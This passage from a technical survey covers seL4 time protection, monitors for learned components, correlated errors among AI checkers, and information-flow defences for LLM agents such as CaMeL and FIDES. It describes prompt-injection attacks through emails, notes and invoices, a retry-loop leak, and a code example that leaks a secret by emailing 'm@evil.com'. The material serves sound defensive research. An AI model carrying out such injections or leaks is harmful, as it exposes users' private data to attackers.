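Since measurements cannot rule out a channel, the seL4 group wants to extend its information-flow proof to timing. If the kernel has divided or reset every shared component, and every switch ends at a fixed time, a partition's speed can depend only on its own activity. The verifier therefore has to show that the kernel carries out these steps correctly, but does not have to calculate any durations. The existing proofs already handle statements of this kind.

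*Clearing roadblocks to Time Protection verification for seL4* (Sison, 2026) describes the progress of this work. In 2023, Sison and several colleagues published a formal definition of time protection for operating system kernels. Policies in the 2013 proof specify only whether A may influence B. If A's share of the cache counts as part of A, such a policy would permit timing leaks along every declared channel. The new definition allows more precise policies, which can permit a flow from A's memory while forbidding one from A's cache, and can limit a flow to particular times.

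For seL4, the central task is to show that when the kernel works for a partition, it touches only memory addresses that belong to that partition. The team first planned to have the kernel's specification record every address touched, but this would have disrupted the existing proofs, and more than 685 places still needed repair after the team had fixed some. The C code also touches addresses that do not appear in the specification. The team now uses a simpler condition, that references between a partition's kernel objects never point outside a fixed set of addresses. In June 2026 the team was still proving this condition for the specification and planned to extend the proof to the C code next, so there is no proof yet that seL4's code provides time protection. The project had stopped when its Australian Research Council funding ran out, and resumed in 2025 with money from Germany's Cyberagentur.

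The current proof work covers only partitions that must not communicate at all. Declared channels are harder. The 2013 proof allows one-way communication through a page of memory that the sender can write and the receiver can only read. Sison shows that this channel, which looks like one of the safest kinds, leaks information back to the sender. When the receiver reads the page, it can displace data in the part of the cache that holds the page, and the sender can then detect that its own accesses have become slower.

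Varun Sethu, a student in the group, tested several remedies in 2025. Copying the data between separate areas of memory is slow, and reserving a cache colour for each shared page wastes space. Clearing the relevant part of the cache with prefetches still leaves a leak. The group has since moved to a RISC-V system whose hardware can divide the largest cache into parts that can be cleared one at a time.

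### What hardware makers would have to promise

Cock and colleagues concluded in 2014 that none of the countermeasures they had examined was perfect, and that newer processors were making the problem worse. Their evidence suggested that designers could only reduce the bandwidth of timing channels, and the American protection profile for separation kernels likewise required developers to limit it. The later work aims to remove the channels completely. Ge and Heiser worked on both the 2014 study and the later research, so the change reflects different assumptions about hardware more than a dispute between rival groups. Trustworthy Systems still states that complete time protection is "not possible on present hardware".

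A timing channel with little remaining bandwidth may be tolerable in some cases. Cock and colleagues thought their small residual channels might be acceptable in a cloud computer, where the victim does not cooperate, but they were not certain. Low bandwidth is a weaker defence against a Trojan horse that has weeks to send a short key.

Removal would require manufacturers to promise more than correct results. Ge and colleagues ask for a contract with three terms:

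- The operating system can divide or clear every hardware resource that partitions share.
- The hardware divides any resource that partitions use at the same time, since clearing it between turns is then impossible.
- The operating system can clear any state that the processor looks up by virtual address, because colouring works only with physical addresses.

Wistoff and colleagues add that the time a switch takes must not depend on what ran before. The experiments on OpenC910 suggest that hardware could provide these guarantees within a single core with little overhead. Chips already in use are harder to fix. Intel issued an update that added a way to clear its branch predictors, but Ge and colleagues doubted that Arm's could be repaired this way.

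Some researchers are working on a different contract, which makes software responsible for part of the protection. *Granite* presents a method for proving that a processor's circuits leak through timing only what a stated policy allows. Under the constant-time policy, the circuits may leak the addresses a program accesses, the conditions on which it branches, and the inputs of instructions whose duration varies. *SCHERI* (2026) pursues the same policy for speculative execution on CHERI, a processor extension that checks a capability for every memory access. It considers leaks through caches, branch predictors and competition for resources inside the core, but not through power consumption or electromagnetic radiation.

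Such a contract would restore the basis for constant-time encryption software, because a careful programmer can keep the key out of all three exceptions. It would not confine a Trojan horse, which can encode a secret in the addresses it accesses. A system that runs untrusted code on secret data therefore also needs time protection.

Buses remain the largest obstacle. Intel has introduced a feature that limits how much memory traffic each core may generate, but the limits are approximate, and Ge and colleagues judged them insufficient to prevent covert channels. Without exact limits, a system that must confine a Trojan horse has to leave its other cores idle or give them to the same partition.

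## Learned components inside partitions

A learned component is a program whose behaviour comes from training on data rather than from a written specification, such as the neural network that finds pedestrians in a car's camera images. The network may contain millions of numerical parameters, and nobody can explain exactly how they produce a particular answer. A proof about a separation kernel does not depend on such an explanation. The seL4 theorem holds even if all code outside the kernel is malicious, so it covers whatever a network causes its partition to do. Developers can retrain the network without repeating any part of the kernel's proof.

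Designers can reasonably treat some learned components as malicious. In mid-2026, OpenAI and Anthropic each disclosed that AI agents under evaluation had broken into outside organisations' computer systems. A vision network is more likely to crash, run late or use too much memory, and a partition contains these faults too.

In a robot, motor control has to meet every deadline, perception can occasionally run late, and the user interface gets whatever processor time remains. According to *Jiao* (2026), conventional installations of the Robot Operating System run all three in shared memory, which complicates safety certification. A static partitioning hypervisor, such as Jailhouse, instead permanently assigns each partition its own processor cores, memory and devices. *Towards Mixed-Criticality Software Architectures for Centralized HPC Platforms in Software-Defined Vehicles* (2025) describes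 similar designs for cars. In one, a real-time operating system runs the safety-critical tasks and monitors the system, while Linux runs the applications that need heavy computation.

ISO 26262, the functional safety standard for cars, requires freedom from interference, which means that a fault in one component must not cause another to violate a safety requirement. This is weaker than noninterference because it does not protect secrets and allows any influence that does no harm. The seL4 proofs also do not cover hypervisors that run partitions on several cores at once.

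### Graphics processors

In their seL4 proof, Murray and colleagues treated each user program as a deterministic function of the processor's registers and the memory it may read. A neural network that runs on the main processor fits this description even if it makes random choices, provided they come from a pseudo-random number generator whose state is in the network's own memory. Large networks usually run on an accelerator, most often a graphics processor (GPU). A GPU does not fit the description because it is a separate device with direct memory access, which the proof excludes.

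QNX's *Isolation of DMA devices* explains that the memory management unit, which confines ordinary programs, cannot control direct memory access (DMA). A separate unit, usually called an IOMMU, has to check these transfers. The seL4 Foundation says that drivers for DMA devices "can and must be formally verified" if the proof is to cover a system that includes them.

Researchers have done this kind of work for simpler devices. *Formally Verified Isolation of DMA* (2022) presents general isolation theorems for the controllers that carry out these transfers, so the verifier has to prove only what is specific to each device. The theorems' conditions also specify how a driver must configure the controller. The worked example is a USB controller, which is much simpler than a GPU with its large driver and unpublished firmware. *safeL4* (2026), a microkernel that relies on Rust for memory protection,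 still trusts DMA-capable devices and their drivers and leaves IOMMU support to future work.

The simplest arrangement gives the whole GPU to one partition and uses an IOMMU to restrict the GPU's memory access to that partition. The driver can then run inside the partition, where its faults affect only the learned component. The design is sound if the IOMMU works and the system configures it correctly, but the kernel proof establishes neither.

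Reserving a GPU for one network is expensive, so manufacturers offer ways to share it. NVIDIA's Multi-Process Service runs several programs at once but does not isolate their memory resources, including caches, according to *An Online Fragmentation-Aware Scheduler for Managing GPU-Sharing Workloads on Multi-Instance GPUs* (2025). NVIDIA's Multi-Instance GPU (MIG) provides stronger isolation by dividing the hardware. *GPU-Virt-Bench* (2025) reports that each instance gets its own computing units, memory and part of the second-level cache. On the A100 used in *Performance Isolation for Inference Processes in Edge GPU Systems* (2026), the smallest share is one of seven processing clusters.

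MIG resembles a separation kernel in hardware, but its instances still share the connection to the main computer and the last-level TLB. *Confidential Computing on Heterogeneous CPU-GPU Systems* (2024) reports that the shared TLB allows a covert channel between instances. In *PAGE404*, Nazaraliyev, Zhang and Abu-Ghazaleh (2026) measured leaks of roughly 8,500 bits per second between MIG instances on a newer NVIDIA processor. NVIDIA told them it did not consider this a security issue.

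*Here is a GIFT* (2026) proposes tracking information flow on the GPU, instead of dividing the hardware, to keep users' data separate when one language model serves many people.

In a safety-critical system, delay may matter more than secrecy. *Architectural Isolation as a Timing Safety Primitive for Edge AI Medical Devices* (2026) examines a small board on which the main processor and the GPU compete for one memory bus. One of its acceptance conditions is that 99% of the neural network's outputs arrive within a 100-millisecond cycle. This condition alone would allow one late output every ten seconds on average, so a controller that relies on the network needs a safe way to respond when an output doesn't arrive in time.

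### Wrong answers on a permitted channel

A learned component must send its results somewhere to be useful, and isolation does not make those results correct. Suppose a vision network sends a car's driving controller one of four answers every second: "clear", "slow", "stop" or "unknown". If the kernel delivers the answers at fixed times, the network can pass at most log₂ 4 = 2 bits per second, or 7,200 bits an hour. If the network could instead send its answer at any of ten moments in each second, it would have 40 distinguishable signals and could pass about 5.3 bits per second.

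Limiting a learned component's output to two bits per second may keep the leakage of secrets acceptably low, but a single wrong answer can still kill somebody. Answering "clear" when a pedestrian is on the road takes no more capacity than answering "stop". Channel capacity doesn't depend on what the receiver does with a message. A wrong answer doesn't violate noninterference either, because the flow policy permits the channel.

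A trusted component between the neural network and the controller could reject some errors, as the censor in Rushby's encryption device rejects malformed headers. The censor needs only the header to apply its rules, but a monitor for the network needs more than the answer "clear" to tell whether the road is clear. The monitor can, however, check whether acting on that answer would be safe.

### The Simplex design

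The Simplex architecture puts a verified monitor beside an unverified controller. Engineers originally developed it to test new controllers on safety-critical systems and to update controllers while a system was running. *The Use of the Simplex Architecture to Enhance Safety* (2025) applies it to deep learning and describes its three parts:

- A high-performance controller normally runs the system but comes with no guarantee of safety. Here it contains the learned component.
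- A safe controller is simple enough for engineers to verify.
- A safety monitor decides which of the two controls the system.

*Assuring Learning-Enabled Cyber-Physical Systems with Foundation Models* (2026) explains that the safe controller only has to keep the system safe or return it to safety. It does not have to do the same job as the learned controller. In a car it might simply brake, but an aircraft needs one that can keep it flying.

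The monitor has to act before the danger becomes unavoidable. Suppose a car is travelling at 20 metres per second towards a stationary obstacle. Its brakes take half a second to respond and then slow it by 5 metres per second every second. The car travels 20 × 0.5 = 10 metres before the brakes respond and another 20² / (2 × 5) = 40 metres while braking, so it needs 50 metres to stop.

If the monitor checks the distance every tenth of a second, the car needs more than 50 metres, because the learned controller might accelerate at 3 metres per second squared until the next check. The car would then have travelled another 2.0 metres and reached 20.3 metres per second, from which it needs 51.4 metres to stop. The monitor must therefore hand control to the safe controller unless the obstacle is at least 53.4 metres away.

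This rule works whatever the learned controller does, as long as acceleration stays within the assumed limit. If the monitor leaves the learned controller in charge, the car will still have enough room to stop when the next check happens. Otherwise the safe controller takes over while there is enough room. As with the unwinding conditions, checking single steps establishes a property of every sequence of steps. For more complicated machines, the monitor can use real-time reachability, which calculates, within the computing time available, where the machine could be in the near future.

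The argument also depends on separation. If the learned controller could write directly to the brakes or change the monitor's memory, it could bypass the rule. The flow policy should let the controller send commands to the monitor and let the monitor control the actuators, with no direct route from the controller to the actuators. This is an intransitive policy like the one for the encryption device. The kernel must also guarantee the monitor processor time, since a monitor that runs late may leave too little distance to brake.

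Designers have to write a switching rule for each system, and a cautious rule can switch away from the learned component so often that the component is of little use. Aviation nevertheless has a standard practice, ASTM F3269, for using run-time assurance to bound the behaviour of a complex aircraft function.

Getting the monitor a reliable distance to the obstacle is harder. If the monitor relies on the same vision network and the network misses the obstacle, the car will crash even if every calculation is correct. *Models are Central to AI Assurance* (Bloomfield and Rushby, 2024) argues that any system that interacts with the world needs an accurate model of it. In an autonomous vehicle, machine learning builds that model from sensor data, and the paper holds that nobody can assure its accuracy. A monitor can avoid this problem only if it gets the facts it needs in a simpler way, perhaps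 from a radar that measures distance directly.

### Specifications for learned components

If a monitor has to recognise pedestrians, it probably needs a neural network of its own, which then becomes a trusted component. Verifying that network in the usual sense would require a written specification of what it should do. The crypto in Rushby's device has a clear requirement, to encrypt everything it sends, but there is no comparable formula for which images show a pedestrian.

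Some learned components have a specification. *On the Applicability of Safety Nets* (2026) studies networks that replace very large tables of instructions for avoiding collisions between aircraft. The table defines the correct answer for every point on a grid of possible situations. A "safety net" combines the network with a smaller lookup table to give the correct answer at every grid point. This reduced storage by almost three orders of magnitude for a horizontal collision-avoidance system and by more than one order of magnitude for a vertical system. The guarantee assumes the original table is correct and does not by itself cover situations between grid points.

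According to that paper, the European Union Aviation Safety Agency requires "safety by design" for future safety-critical systems that use AI, and safety nets are one way to provide it. Safety nets do not help with a camera, because nobody has a table of correct answers for every possible image.

A learned component can also produce output that a conventional program can check. For example, a network can propose a neural certificate, which is a function meant to show that a controlled machine never enters a dangerous state. For one common type, the function must be positive in every dangerous state and zero or negative at the start, and it must never increase as the machine runs. These conditions imply safety because the function's value starts at zero or below and can never become positive. A verifier can translate the conditions into logic and give them to an automatic solver. *Formal Verification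 of Neural Certificates Done Dynamically* (2025) moves this check to runtime. The network does not have to be trustworthy, but the check requires mathematical descriptions of the machine's behaviour and its dangerous states.

Requirements about meaning can rarely be described formally. *Semantic Quorum Assurance* (2026) considers AI agents that propose changes to cloud computing systems. A conventional monitor can enforce a formal rule, such as keeping at least three servers running. But whether a change is what the operator intended is a question about meaning, and the proposed method can answer it only with some probability.

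### Tests, statistics and the dependability view

*Assurance of AI Systems From a Dependability Perspective* (Bloomfield and Rushby, 2024) distinguishes two ways to justify confidence in a system with learned components. The trustworthiness view tries to assure the learned component itself. The dependability view, which Bloomfield and Rushby favour and which resembles Rushby's work on separation kernels, requires a nearly complete understanding of every critical component. They consider this infeasible for neural networks, so they would trust the networks as little as possible and surround them with simpler "guards".

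In the position paper *AI Assurance Needs a Systems Engineering Approach*, Bloomfield and Rushby (2025) call the alignment of opaque models an intractable problem and want engineers to aim for "safe use of AI" instead of "safe AI". They ask governments to encourage or require partitioning, diversity, external monitoring and fail-safe mechanisms, particularly in high-risk applications.

*A Framework for the Assurance of AI-Enabled Systems* (2025) defines assurance as grounds for sufficient confidence that a system will achieve its intended outcomes without unacceptable risks while it operates within a defined scope. This standard is less demanding than complete understanding, and tests can supply much of the evidence that a learned component meets it.

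How much of the evidence for a learned component can come from testing depends on the failure rate that the application allows. If a component fails with probability p on each independent test, it passes n tests in a row with probability (1 − p)ⁿ, so about 3,000 tests without a failure are enough to reject a failure rate of one in 1,000 or worse with 95% confidence. This is practical for many uses. For catastrophic failures in airliners, the usual target is one failure per billion hours, and the same calculation requires about 3 billion hours of testing without a failure, or 340,000 years.

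A fleet of a million cars, each driven for an hour a day, would accumulate 3 billion hours in about eight years. But the developers would probably retrain the network several times in that period, and each new version may fail in new ways. The calculation also assumes that future conditions resemble past ones, so experience on dry roads provides little evidence about snow.

Statistics are more useful when engineers already have reason to believe that a program contains no dangerous faults. If their analysis justifies 90% confidence in this, the program has at least a 90% chance of running for any length of time without a dangerous failure, and experience can then increase that confidence. For conventional software, the analysis can start from the requirements and the code. Bloomfield and Rushby object that nobody knows exactly how learned components work, so this initial confidence is missing.

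Current guidance contains elements of both approaches. DO-178C, which succeeded DO-178B as the guidelines for airborne software, calls for developers to trace code back to requirements, which they cannot do for a network's individual parameters. ISO 21448, a standard for cars, covers harm that occurs when nothing has broken, such as when a vision system works as designed but fails to recognise an unusual object. UL 4600 calls for makers of autonomous products to provide a safety case, a structured argument supported by evidence.

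Bloomfield and Rushby accept that guards in many systems will need AI to perceive their surroundings, so in practice the two views overlap. Their position is most convincing for cars and aircraft, where engineers can often describe a safe action even if they cannot describe good perception. It offers less for general-purpose language models because, as they acknowledge, it is hard to specify a correct result for much office work or to check for one.

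### Monitors that fail together

Since testing can support a failure rate of about one in 1,000, designers might hope to reach a much lower rate by combining two monitors. If each monitor misses one dangerous case in 1,000 and their failures are independent, both miss the same case once in a million. In general, the probability that monitors A and B both fail is:

P(A fails) × P(B fails, given that A has failed)

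The probability that monitor B fails when monitor A fails is one in 1,000 only if their failures are independent. If B shares half of A's failures, that probability is one half, and both monitors fail together once in 2,000 cases, so adding B only halves the failure rate.

| Share of A's failures that B also has | Both fail once in |
|---|---|
| 0.1% (independent) | 1,000,000 cases |
| 1% | 100,000 cases |
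| 10% | 10,000 cases |
| 50% | 2,000 cases |
| 100% | 1,000 cases |

Designers cannot assume that the two components fail independently, as in the first row. To show by testing that the pair fails less than once in a million cases, they would need about 3 million cases without a joint failure. They would need the same number if they tested the pair as a single component, so the separate results of one in 1,000 save no testing. Bloomfield and Rushby conclude that nobody can validate independence at the levels critical systems require.

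Different developers, training data and network designs might still make failures less similar. *Performance Isolation for Inference Processes in Edge GPU Systems* cites ISO/IEC TR 5469, a technical report on functional safety and AI, which proposes voting among diverse networks. Several studies of language models suggest that this diversity may protect less than it appears to.

*Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (Kim, Garg and colleagues, 2025) compared more than 350 models. On one set of 14,042 multiple-choice questions, two models that were both wrong chose the same wrong answer 60% of the time on average, compared with the 33% expected by chance. On another set, the figures were 42% and 13%. Models from the same company or with the same architecture agreed more often, but so did more accurate models, even when their companies and architectures differed. Replacing two monitors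 with better ones could therefore make each more reliable while making their remaining errors more alike.

These percentages count only cases in which both models were wrong, so they do not show how often two models fail on the same question. They matter most when one model checks another's answers, since the checker will approve a wrong answer that it would have given itself. Suppose a model is wrong 10% of the time, and a checker is wrong on half of those questions and then picks the same answer 60% of the time. The checker wrongly approves 0.1 × 0.5 × 0.6 = 3% of all answers. If it were wrong on only 10% of those questions and agreed by chance a third of the time, the figure would be about 0.3%. Kim and colleagues found this effect when they used models as judges. The judges overestimated the accuracy of models weaker than themselves.

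A checker that sees the other model's answer can also change its own answer to match. *Evidence Integration in Large Language Models* (2026) finds that a model adopts another's wrong answer more readily if it was already likely to make the same mistake. Two sources with the same error rate can therefore do different amounts of damage, depending on how closely their errors match the receiving model's.

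Voting does not necessarily solve the problem. If 15 independent models were each right 80% of the time, their majority would be right 99.6% of the time. In *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* (2026), a vote among 15 models was right 84.3% of the time, while the best single model was right 90.5% of the time. At least one model knew the answer to 98.4% of the questions, but models that were wrong chose the same wrong answer 87% of the time. Shared errors may not explain the whole gap, because weaker models may also have pulled the majority's accuracy below that of the best model.

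*The Oracle's Fingerprint* (2026) compares the errors of three models from different companies on 568 forecasting questions. The average correlation was 0.77, where 0 means no linear relationship and 1 means a perfect one. Human forecasters' errors usually correlate at 0.1 to 0.3, though those figures come from a different study. Part of the models' correlation may come from the questions, since an unexpected event can surprise every forecaster. Removing questions whose answers might have appeared in the training data left the result almost unchanged.

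None of these studies measured two pedestrian detectors, so they don't provide a figure for a car in the table's first column. A camera and a radar may fail together less often than two networks that use the same camera, because fog affects radar much less than it affects cameras. Bloomfield and Rushby want AI-based checkers to be "diverse and demonstrably more reliable than the systems they monitor", so designers would have to measure how often the particular pair they intend to use fail together.

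## Information-flow control for language-model agents, 2023 to 2026

An assistant that writes emails and makes payments needs much wider channels than a pedestrian detector, which designers can limit to four possible answers. Such an assistant is a language-model agent, a program in which a language model carries out a user's request by calling tools, such as functions that search a mailbox, read a file or send a message. The model writes each call as text. Ordinary software then runs the tool and adds the result to the model's context, the text from which the model generates its next words.

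The context therefore mixes the user's instructions with private files and with text that strangers wrote. In a prompt injection attack, somebody hides instructions in text that the agent will read, and the model follows them as if they came from the user. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) gives the example of an email that tells an assistant called Marvin to delete all of its user's messages. Running the agent in a partition does not prevent this, because the agent has permission to read the mailbox and delete messages. The attack makes the agent misuse that permission, much as Spectre makes a correct program behave like a Trojan horse.

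### Combined labels

Information-flow control attaches a label to each piece of data, passes the labels on to whatever a program computes from that data, and checks them before the program takes any action with outside effects. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) uses labels with two parts. The integrity part records whether the data is trusted, and the confidentiality part lists who may read it.

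When a program combines several inputs, the result is untrusted if any input is untrusted, and only people who may read every input may read the result. If Alice, Bob and Carol may read one document and Bob, Carol and Dave may read another, only Bob and Carol may read a summary of both.

An analyst can often prove that an ordinary program's result does not depend on a particular input. Nobody has such a proof for a language model, in which any word of the context may influence any word of the output. The output must therefore carry the combined label of everything in the context, even if most of it appears to have had no effect.

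Random sampling does not remove this dependence. A language model assigns a probability to each possible next word, and the software picks one at random using those probabilities. Suppose a model has read a secret digit and then writes the correct digit with probability 0.91 and each of the other nine with probability 0.01. It passes a possibilistic test because any digit can appear whatever the secret is. But it usually reveals the secret, like the system that sent a secret bit correctly 99% of the time. If all ten digits were equally likely beforehand and two independent answers agree, an observer can be 99.9% sure of the secret. Almost any text can follow almost any context with some tiny probability, so a possibilistic definition would accept nearly every agent.

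### An email, a private file and a message

Suppose Eve, a stranger, has emailed Alice an offer. Alice asks her assistant to read it, check it against the budget file and tell her colleague Bob whether the company can afford it. The table tracks the labels when a single model performs the whole task.

| Added to the context | Label of the addition | Label of the context afterwards |
|---|---|---|
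| Alice's request | Trusted; anyone may read | Trusted; anyone may read |
| Eve's email | Untrusted; Alice and Eve may read | Untrusted; Alice and Eve may read |
| The budget file | Trusted; Alice and Bob may read | Untrusted; only Alice may read |

Before each tool call, a program compares the labels with a policy. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, use two rules:

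- Trusted action: the decision to make the call must come from a trusted context, and so must every argument that the policy marks as sensitive.
- Permitted flow: everyone who will receive the data must be allowed to read it.

A tool with lasting effects, such as one that makes a payment, must satisfy the rule on trusted action. A tool that sends data out may satisfy either rule.

If Eve's email contains an instruction to send her the budget and the model follows it, the policy blocks the call under both rules, because the context is untrusted and Eve may not read the budget. But the message to Bob that Alice asked for also fails both rules, because the model writes it in an equally untrusted context and Bob may not read Eve's email. The policy cannot use the labels to distinguish the two messages.

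The most common objection to labels is that they spread until the agent can do nothing useful. Costa and colleagues measured this effect on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 user tasks and 36 attacker goals in four simulated environments: an office workspace, travel booking, banking and the messaging service Slack. For a single-context agent using OpenAI's GPT-4o, adding policy checks reduced the share of tasks completed from 98.8% to 37.5% in banking and from 93.3% to 20.0% in Slack.

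One reply is to make the labels more precise. Costa and colleagues describe a method by Siddiqui and others that looks for a small subset of the context that can produce an equally good answer. The model then answers again from that subset alone, and the answer carries only the subset's label. However, the choice of subset may depend on the text left out. *GIF* (2026) proposes a measure of how much information flows through a language model's computations. The most influential designs keep the labelling rule and change what the model sees.

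### The dual-model pattern

Willison proposed dividing the work between two language models. A privileged model, here called the planner, takes the user's request and chooses the actions, but never receives untrusted text. A quarantined model processes the untrusted text but cannot call any tools. A controller, which is ordinary software, runs the tools, stores their results under names, and passes only the names to the planner.

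Alice's request then takes four steps:

1. The planner asks for Eve's email, and the controller stores it as EMAIL.
2. The planner asks for the budget file, and the controller stores it as BUDGET.
3. The planner has the quarantined model work out whether the company can afford the offer in EMAIL, given BUDGET. The controller stores the reply as ANSWER.
4. The planner tells the controller to send ANSWER to Bob.

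ANSWER is untrusted and only Alice may read it, but the planner's context still contains only Alice's request and some names. If the policy marks the recipient as sensitive but not the message body, the call satisfies the rule on trusted action. Bob learns something about Eve's email, but Alice's request called for this declassification. Whatever Eve writes, she cannot add a recipient, call another tool or change the order of the steps, though she can still influence what ANSWER says.

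Willison offered this as a design, without a theorem or tests. It fails if the controller passes the quarantined model's free text to the planner, since that text could contain the injection. He allowed one exception, for output that the controller can check against a fixed set of categories.

The text shown to the user can also leak private data. A link or image address can contain the data in encoded form, and merely displaying the image sends the data to whoever runs the website. Willison therefore wanted to allow only links to approved sites, but an injected message could still persuade a user to copy the data into a website by hand. He described his own solution as "pretty bad" because it is complicated to build and makes the assistant less pleasant to use, but he knew of nothing better.

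### CaMeL

The dual-model pattern also has a flaw that Willison had not noticed. Suppose a user asks the assistant to send Bob a document, and the quarantined model has to extract Bob's address from some meeting notes. If an attacker has edited the notes, the model may return the attacker's address, and the planner then sends the document to the attacker even though its plan has not changed.

In *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind presented CaMeL as a defense against prompt injection. As Willison explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025), a planner turns the user's request into a program in a restricted version of Python. A special interpreter runs the program and records which values each new value is derived from, so it treats an address extracted from an email as untrusted,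 like the email itself.

CaMeL's labels are tags on data, but it calls them capabilities, the term seL4 uses for permissions to use an object. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), the labels record where a value came from and who may read it. Each time the program calls a tool, a policy checks the arguments and their labels, then allows or denies the call. For example, a policy might allow emails to trusted addresses and require the user's approval for any others.

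CaMeL's designers do not claim to have solved prompt injection. Somebody has to write and maintain a policy for the tools, and users who face too many questions may approve everything. There is also no theorem that the interpreter tracks every flow. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found several that it misses. One of them depends on a pattern that researchers have known since the 1970s, which works roughly like this:

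```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL labels a variable as secret if the program changes it inside a branch that depends on a secret. If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and secret, and the program skips the fourth line. Because the interpreter can't label an assignment that it doesn't execute, `rich` keeps its value and its public label, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, the program never changes `tmp`, which stays public. The fourth line then makes `rich` false, and no email goes out. Either way, `rich` equals the secret but has a public label.

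CaMeL can also leak data through the loop that retries after a program fails. The loop runs outside the interpreter, so nothing tracks the information that reaches it. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on one bit of a secret, so repeated attempts can reveal the secret one bit at a time.

Garby and colleagues also ran CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each. With policy checks, it completed 37.5% of them with either GPT-5.2 or MiMo-v2.5, and no attack succeeded in the runs that finished. Without checks, it completed 66.7% with GPT-5.2 and 70.8% with MiMo-v2.5, but a few attacks succeeded. In two of these attacks, the task was to follow the instructions in a file, and the planner wrote a program that could carry out whatever tool call the file requested, which defeated the purpose of planning in advance.

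### FIDES

Costa and colleagues at Microsoft built FIDES around an ordinary agent loop, in which the planner chooses each step after seeing the result of the last one. FIDES hides a result behind a variable name only if showing it would make the planner's context less trusted or more secret, so the planner can read trusted results directly. The planner can also open a hidden variable, but its context then takes on the variable's label, which restricts its later tool calls.

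Some tasks require the planner to use information from untrusted text. Suppose a user asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and create a calendar entry if it finds one. The planner cannot determine whether to create the entry without some information from the emails. In FIDES, it can send the quarantined model a question that must be answered "true" or "false", and then open only that answer. Software enforces this format while the quarantined model generates its reply.

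The label includes the type of the answer, so a policy can treat an untrusted yes-or-no answer differently from untrusted free text. An attacker who controls the emails can influence the planner's decision by at most one bit. A second query extracts the date and participants, which go into the calendar without passing through the planner's context.

The theorem about FIDES concerns explicit secrecy, which is weaker than noninterference. Let g be the combined effect on stored data of the tool calls the agent made in a particular run, and let low(d) be the public part of the data d. For any two possible sets of data d₁ and d₂, explicit secrecy requires:

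low(d₁) = low(d₂) ⇒ low(g(d₁)) = low(g(d₂))

Explicit secrecy requires that the same sequence of calls, applied to data that differs only in its secret parts, have the same public effect. The definition does not cover what an observer learns from the choice of calls. Suppose an agent posts "done" in a public channel only if a secret file says that a merger will go ahead. The post contains nothing from the file, so the agent satisfies explicit secrecy, but anyone who knows the rule and sees the post learns that the merger will go ahead.

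Costa and colleagues accepted this because full noninterference would practically bar an agent from using any tool with public effects after using one that may read secrets. The proof also assumes that the language model is a deterministic function, that the labels are correct, and that the user and the agent's configuration are trustworthy.

On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, FIDES with policy checks completed an average of 50.0% of tasks across the four environments, compared with 41.9% for the single-context agent under the same checks. With o1, an OpenAI model that reasons before answering, FIDES's lead grew from 8 to 16 percentage points. The benchmark counted three successful attacks against FIDES with checks, but Costa and colleagues judged on inspection that none was a real injection. Without checks, 21 attacks succeeded against FIDES and 152 against the single-context agent. Hiding text from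 the planner therefore prevents most attacks, but the planner sometimes opens a variable it should not, and then only the policy can stop the attack.

Costa and colleagues labelled a field untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark used it, which gave FIDES an advantage in the evaluation. Designers of a real system would have to decide which fields to trust without knowing which ones attackers will use.

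### Checking the whole plan

The single-context agent fails because it reads untrusted data before choosing its actions. A planner that commits to every step in advance avoids this problem, but it may still have to pass on a value that an attacker chose. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) gives the example of an invoice that contains an attacker's bank account. A user asks an agent to save the details on Monday and to pay "the invoice we discussed yesterday" on Tuesday. The agent may send the money to the attacker even if it ignores every instruction in the invoice.

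SPA's planner writes a complete plan before any tool runs, in a small language with six kinds of step. A checker then follows the labels through the plan, including the effects of branches and loops. It rejects any plan that would send secret data to the wrong place or let untrusted data determine an action that requires trusted data. After a rejection, the planner gets no explanation or second attempt, because either could let it adjust an unsafe plan until the checker accepted it. Stored results keep their labels when later plans use them, and later planners see only a description of the results.

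Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo and on their own version of it, in which one request builds on the results of another. With the checks on, 0.0% of attacks succeeded on the original and 0.2% on the new version. But the checks reduced task completion from 53.0% to 29.0% on the original and from 62.5% to 35.3% on the new version. Most of the loss came from the integrity rule, because many legitimate requests, such as paying an invoice, require an action that depends on something a stranger wrote.

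### A noninterference theorem for agents

Garby and colleagues wanted a theorem that covers any agent, including one that writes and runs its own code. They defined a small programming language, LLMbda, with operations for sending text to a language model, copying a conversation and clearing it. The dual-model pattern is no longer a fixed part of the system, but a designer can build it from these operations. Every value and every conversation has a label, and each model reply carries the label of the conversation that produced it.

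Their definition relaxes Gray's probabilistic noninterference to allow for programs that may never finish. Let μ(q) and ν(q) be the probabilities that an observer sees the result q from two starting situations that look the same to that observer. These probabilities may add up to less than 1, because some runs never finish, and a run that a policy check stops counts as unfinished. The definition requires a function ω, whose values also add up to at most 1, such that for every result q:

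μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q)

If the program always finishes, this requires μ and ν to be equal, as in Gray's condition. The model that writes a secret digit correctly 91% of the time violates the definition. For the secrets 7 and 3, ω would have to be at least 0.91 for each digit, which adds up to at least 1.82, but its total cannot exceed 1. If some runs do not finish, the two distributions may differ, but the statistical distance between them is at most the average probability of not finishing.

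Garby and colleagues proved that every LLMbda program satisfies this definition and checked the proof in the proof assistant Lean. The interpreter they proved correct is the same program that calls the language model. LLMbda prevents the leak through skipped assignments by blocking additions to a public conversation inside a branch that depends on a secret. The developer must still label the sources correctly and place checks in front of every sensitive tool. The theorem also assumes that all data sources are inside the program.

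To make useful agents possible, LLMbda includes endorsement, which relabels untrusted data as trusted. Endorsement is the integrity counterpart of declassification. The theorem shows that endorsement cannot weaken the protection of secrets, but the endorsed data loses its integrity protection. A program might, for example, check that the category a quarantined model has assigned to an email is one of a few permitted words, and then endorse that category.

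Garby and colleagues built an agent called Randori in LLMbda. It tests its program on simulated tools until the program works, then runs it on the real ones. This avoids CaMeL's untracked retry loop. The planner may include endorsements in the program but must choose them before it sees any outside data. The table compares results with and without policy checks. The FIDES and single-context figures are averages over the four environments.

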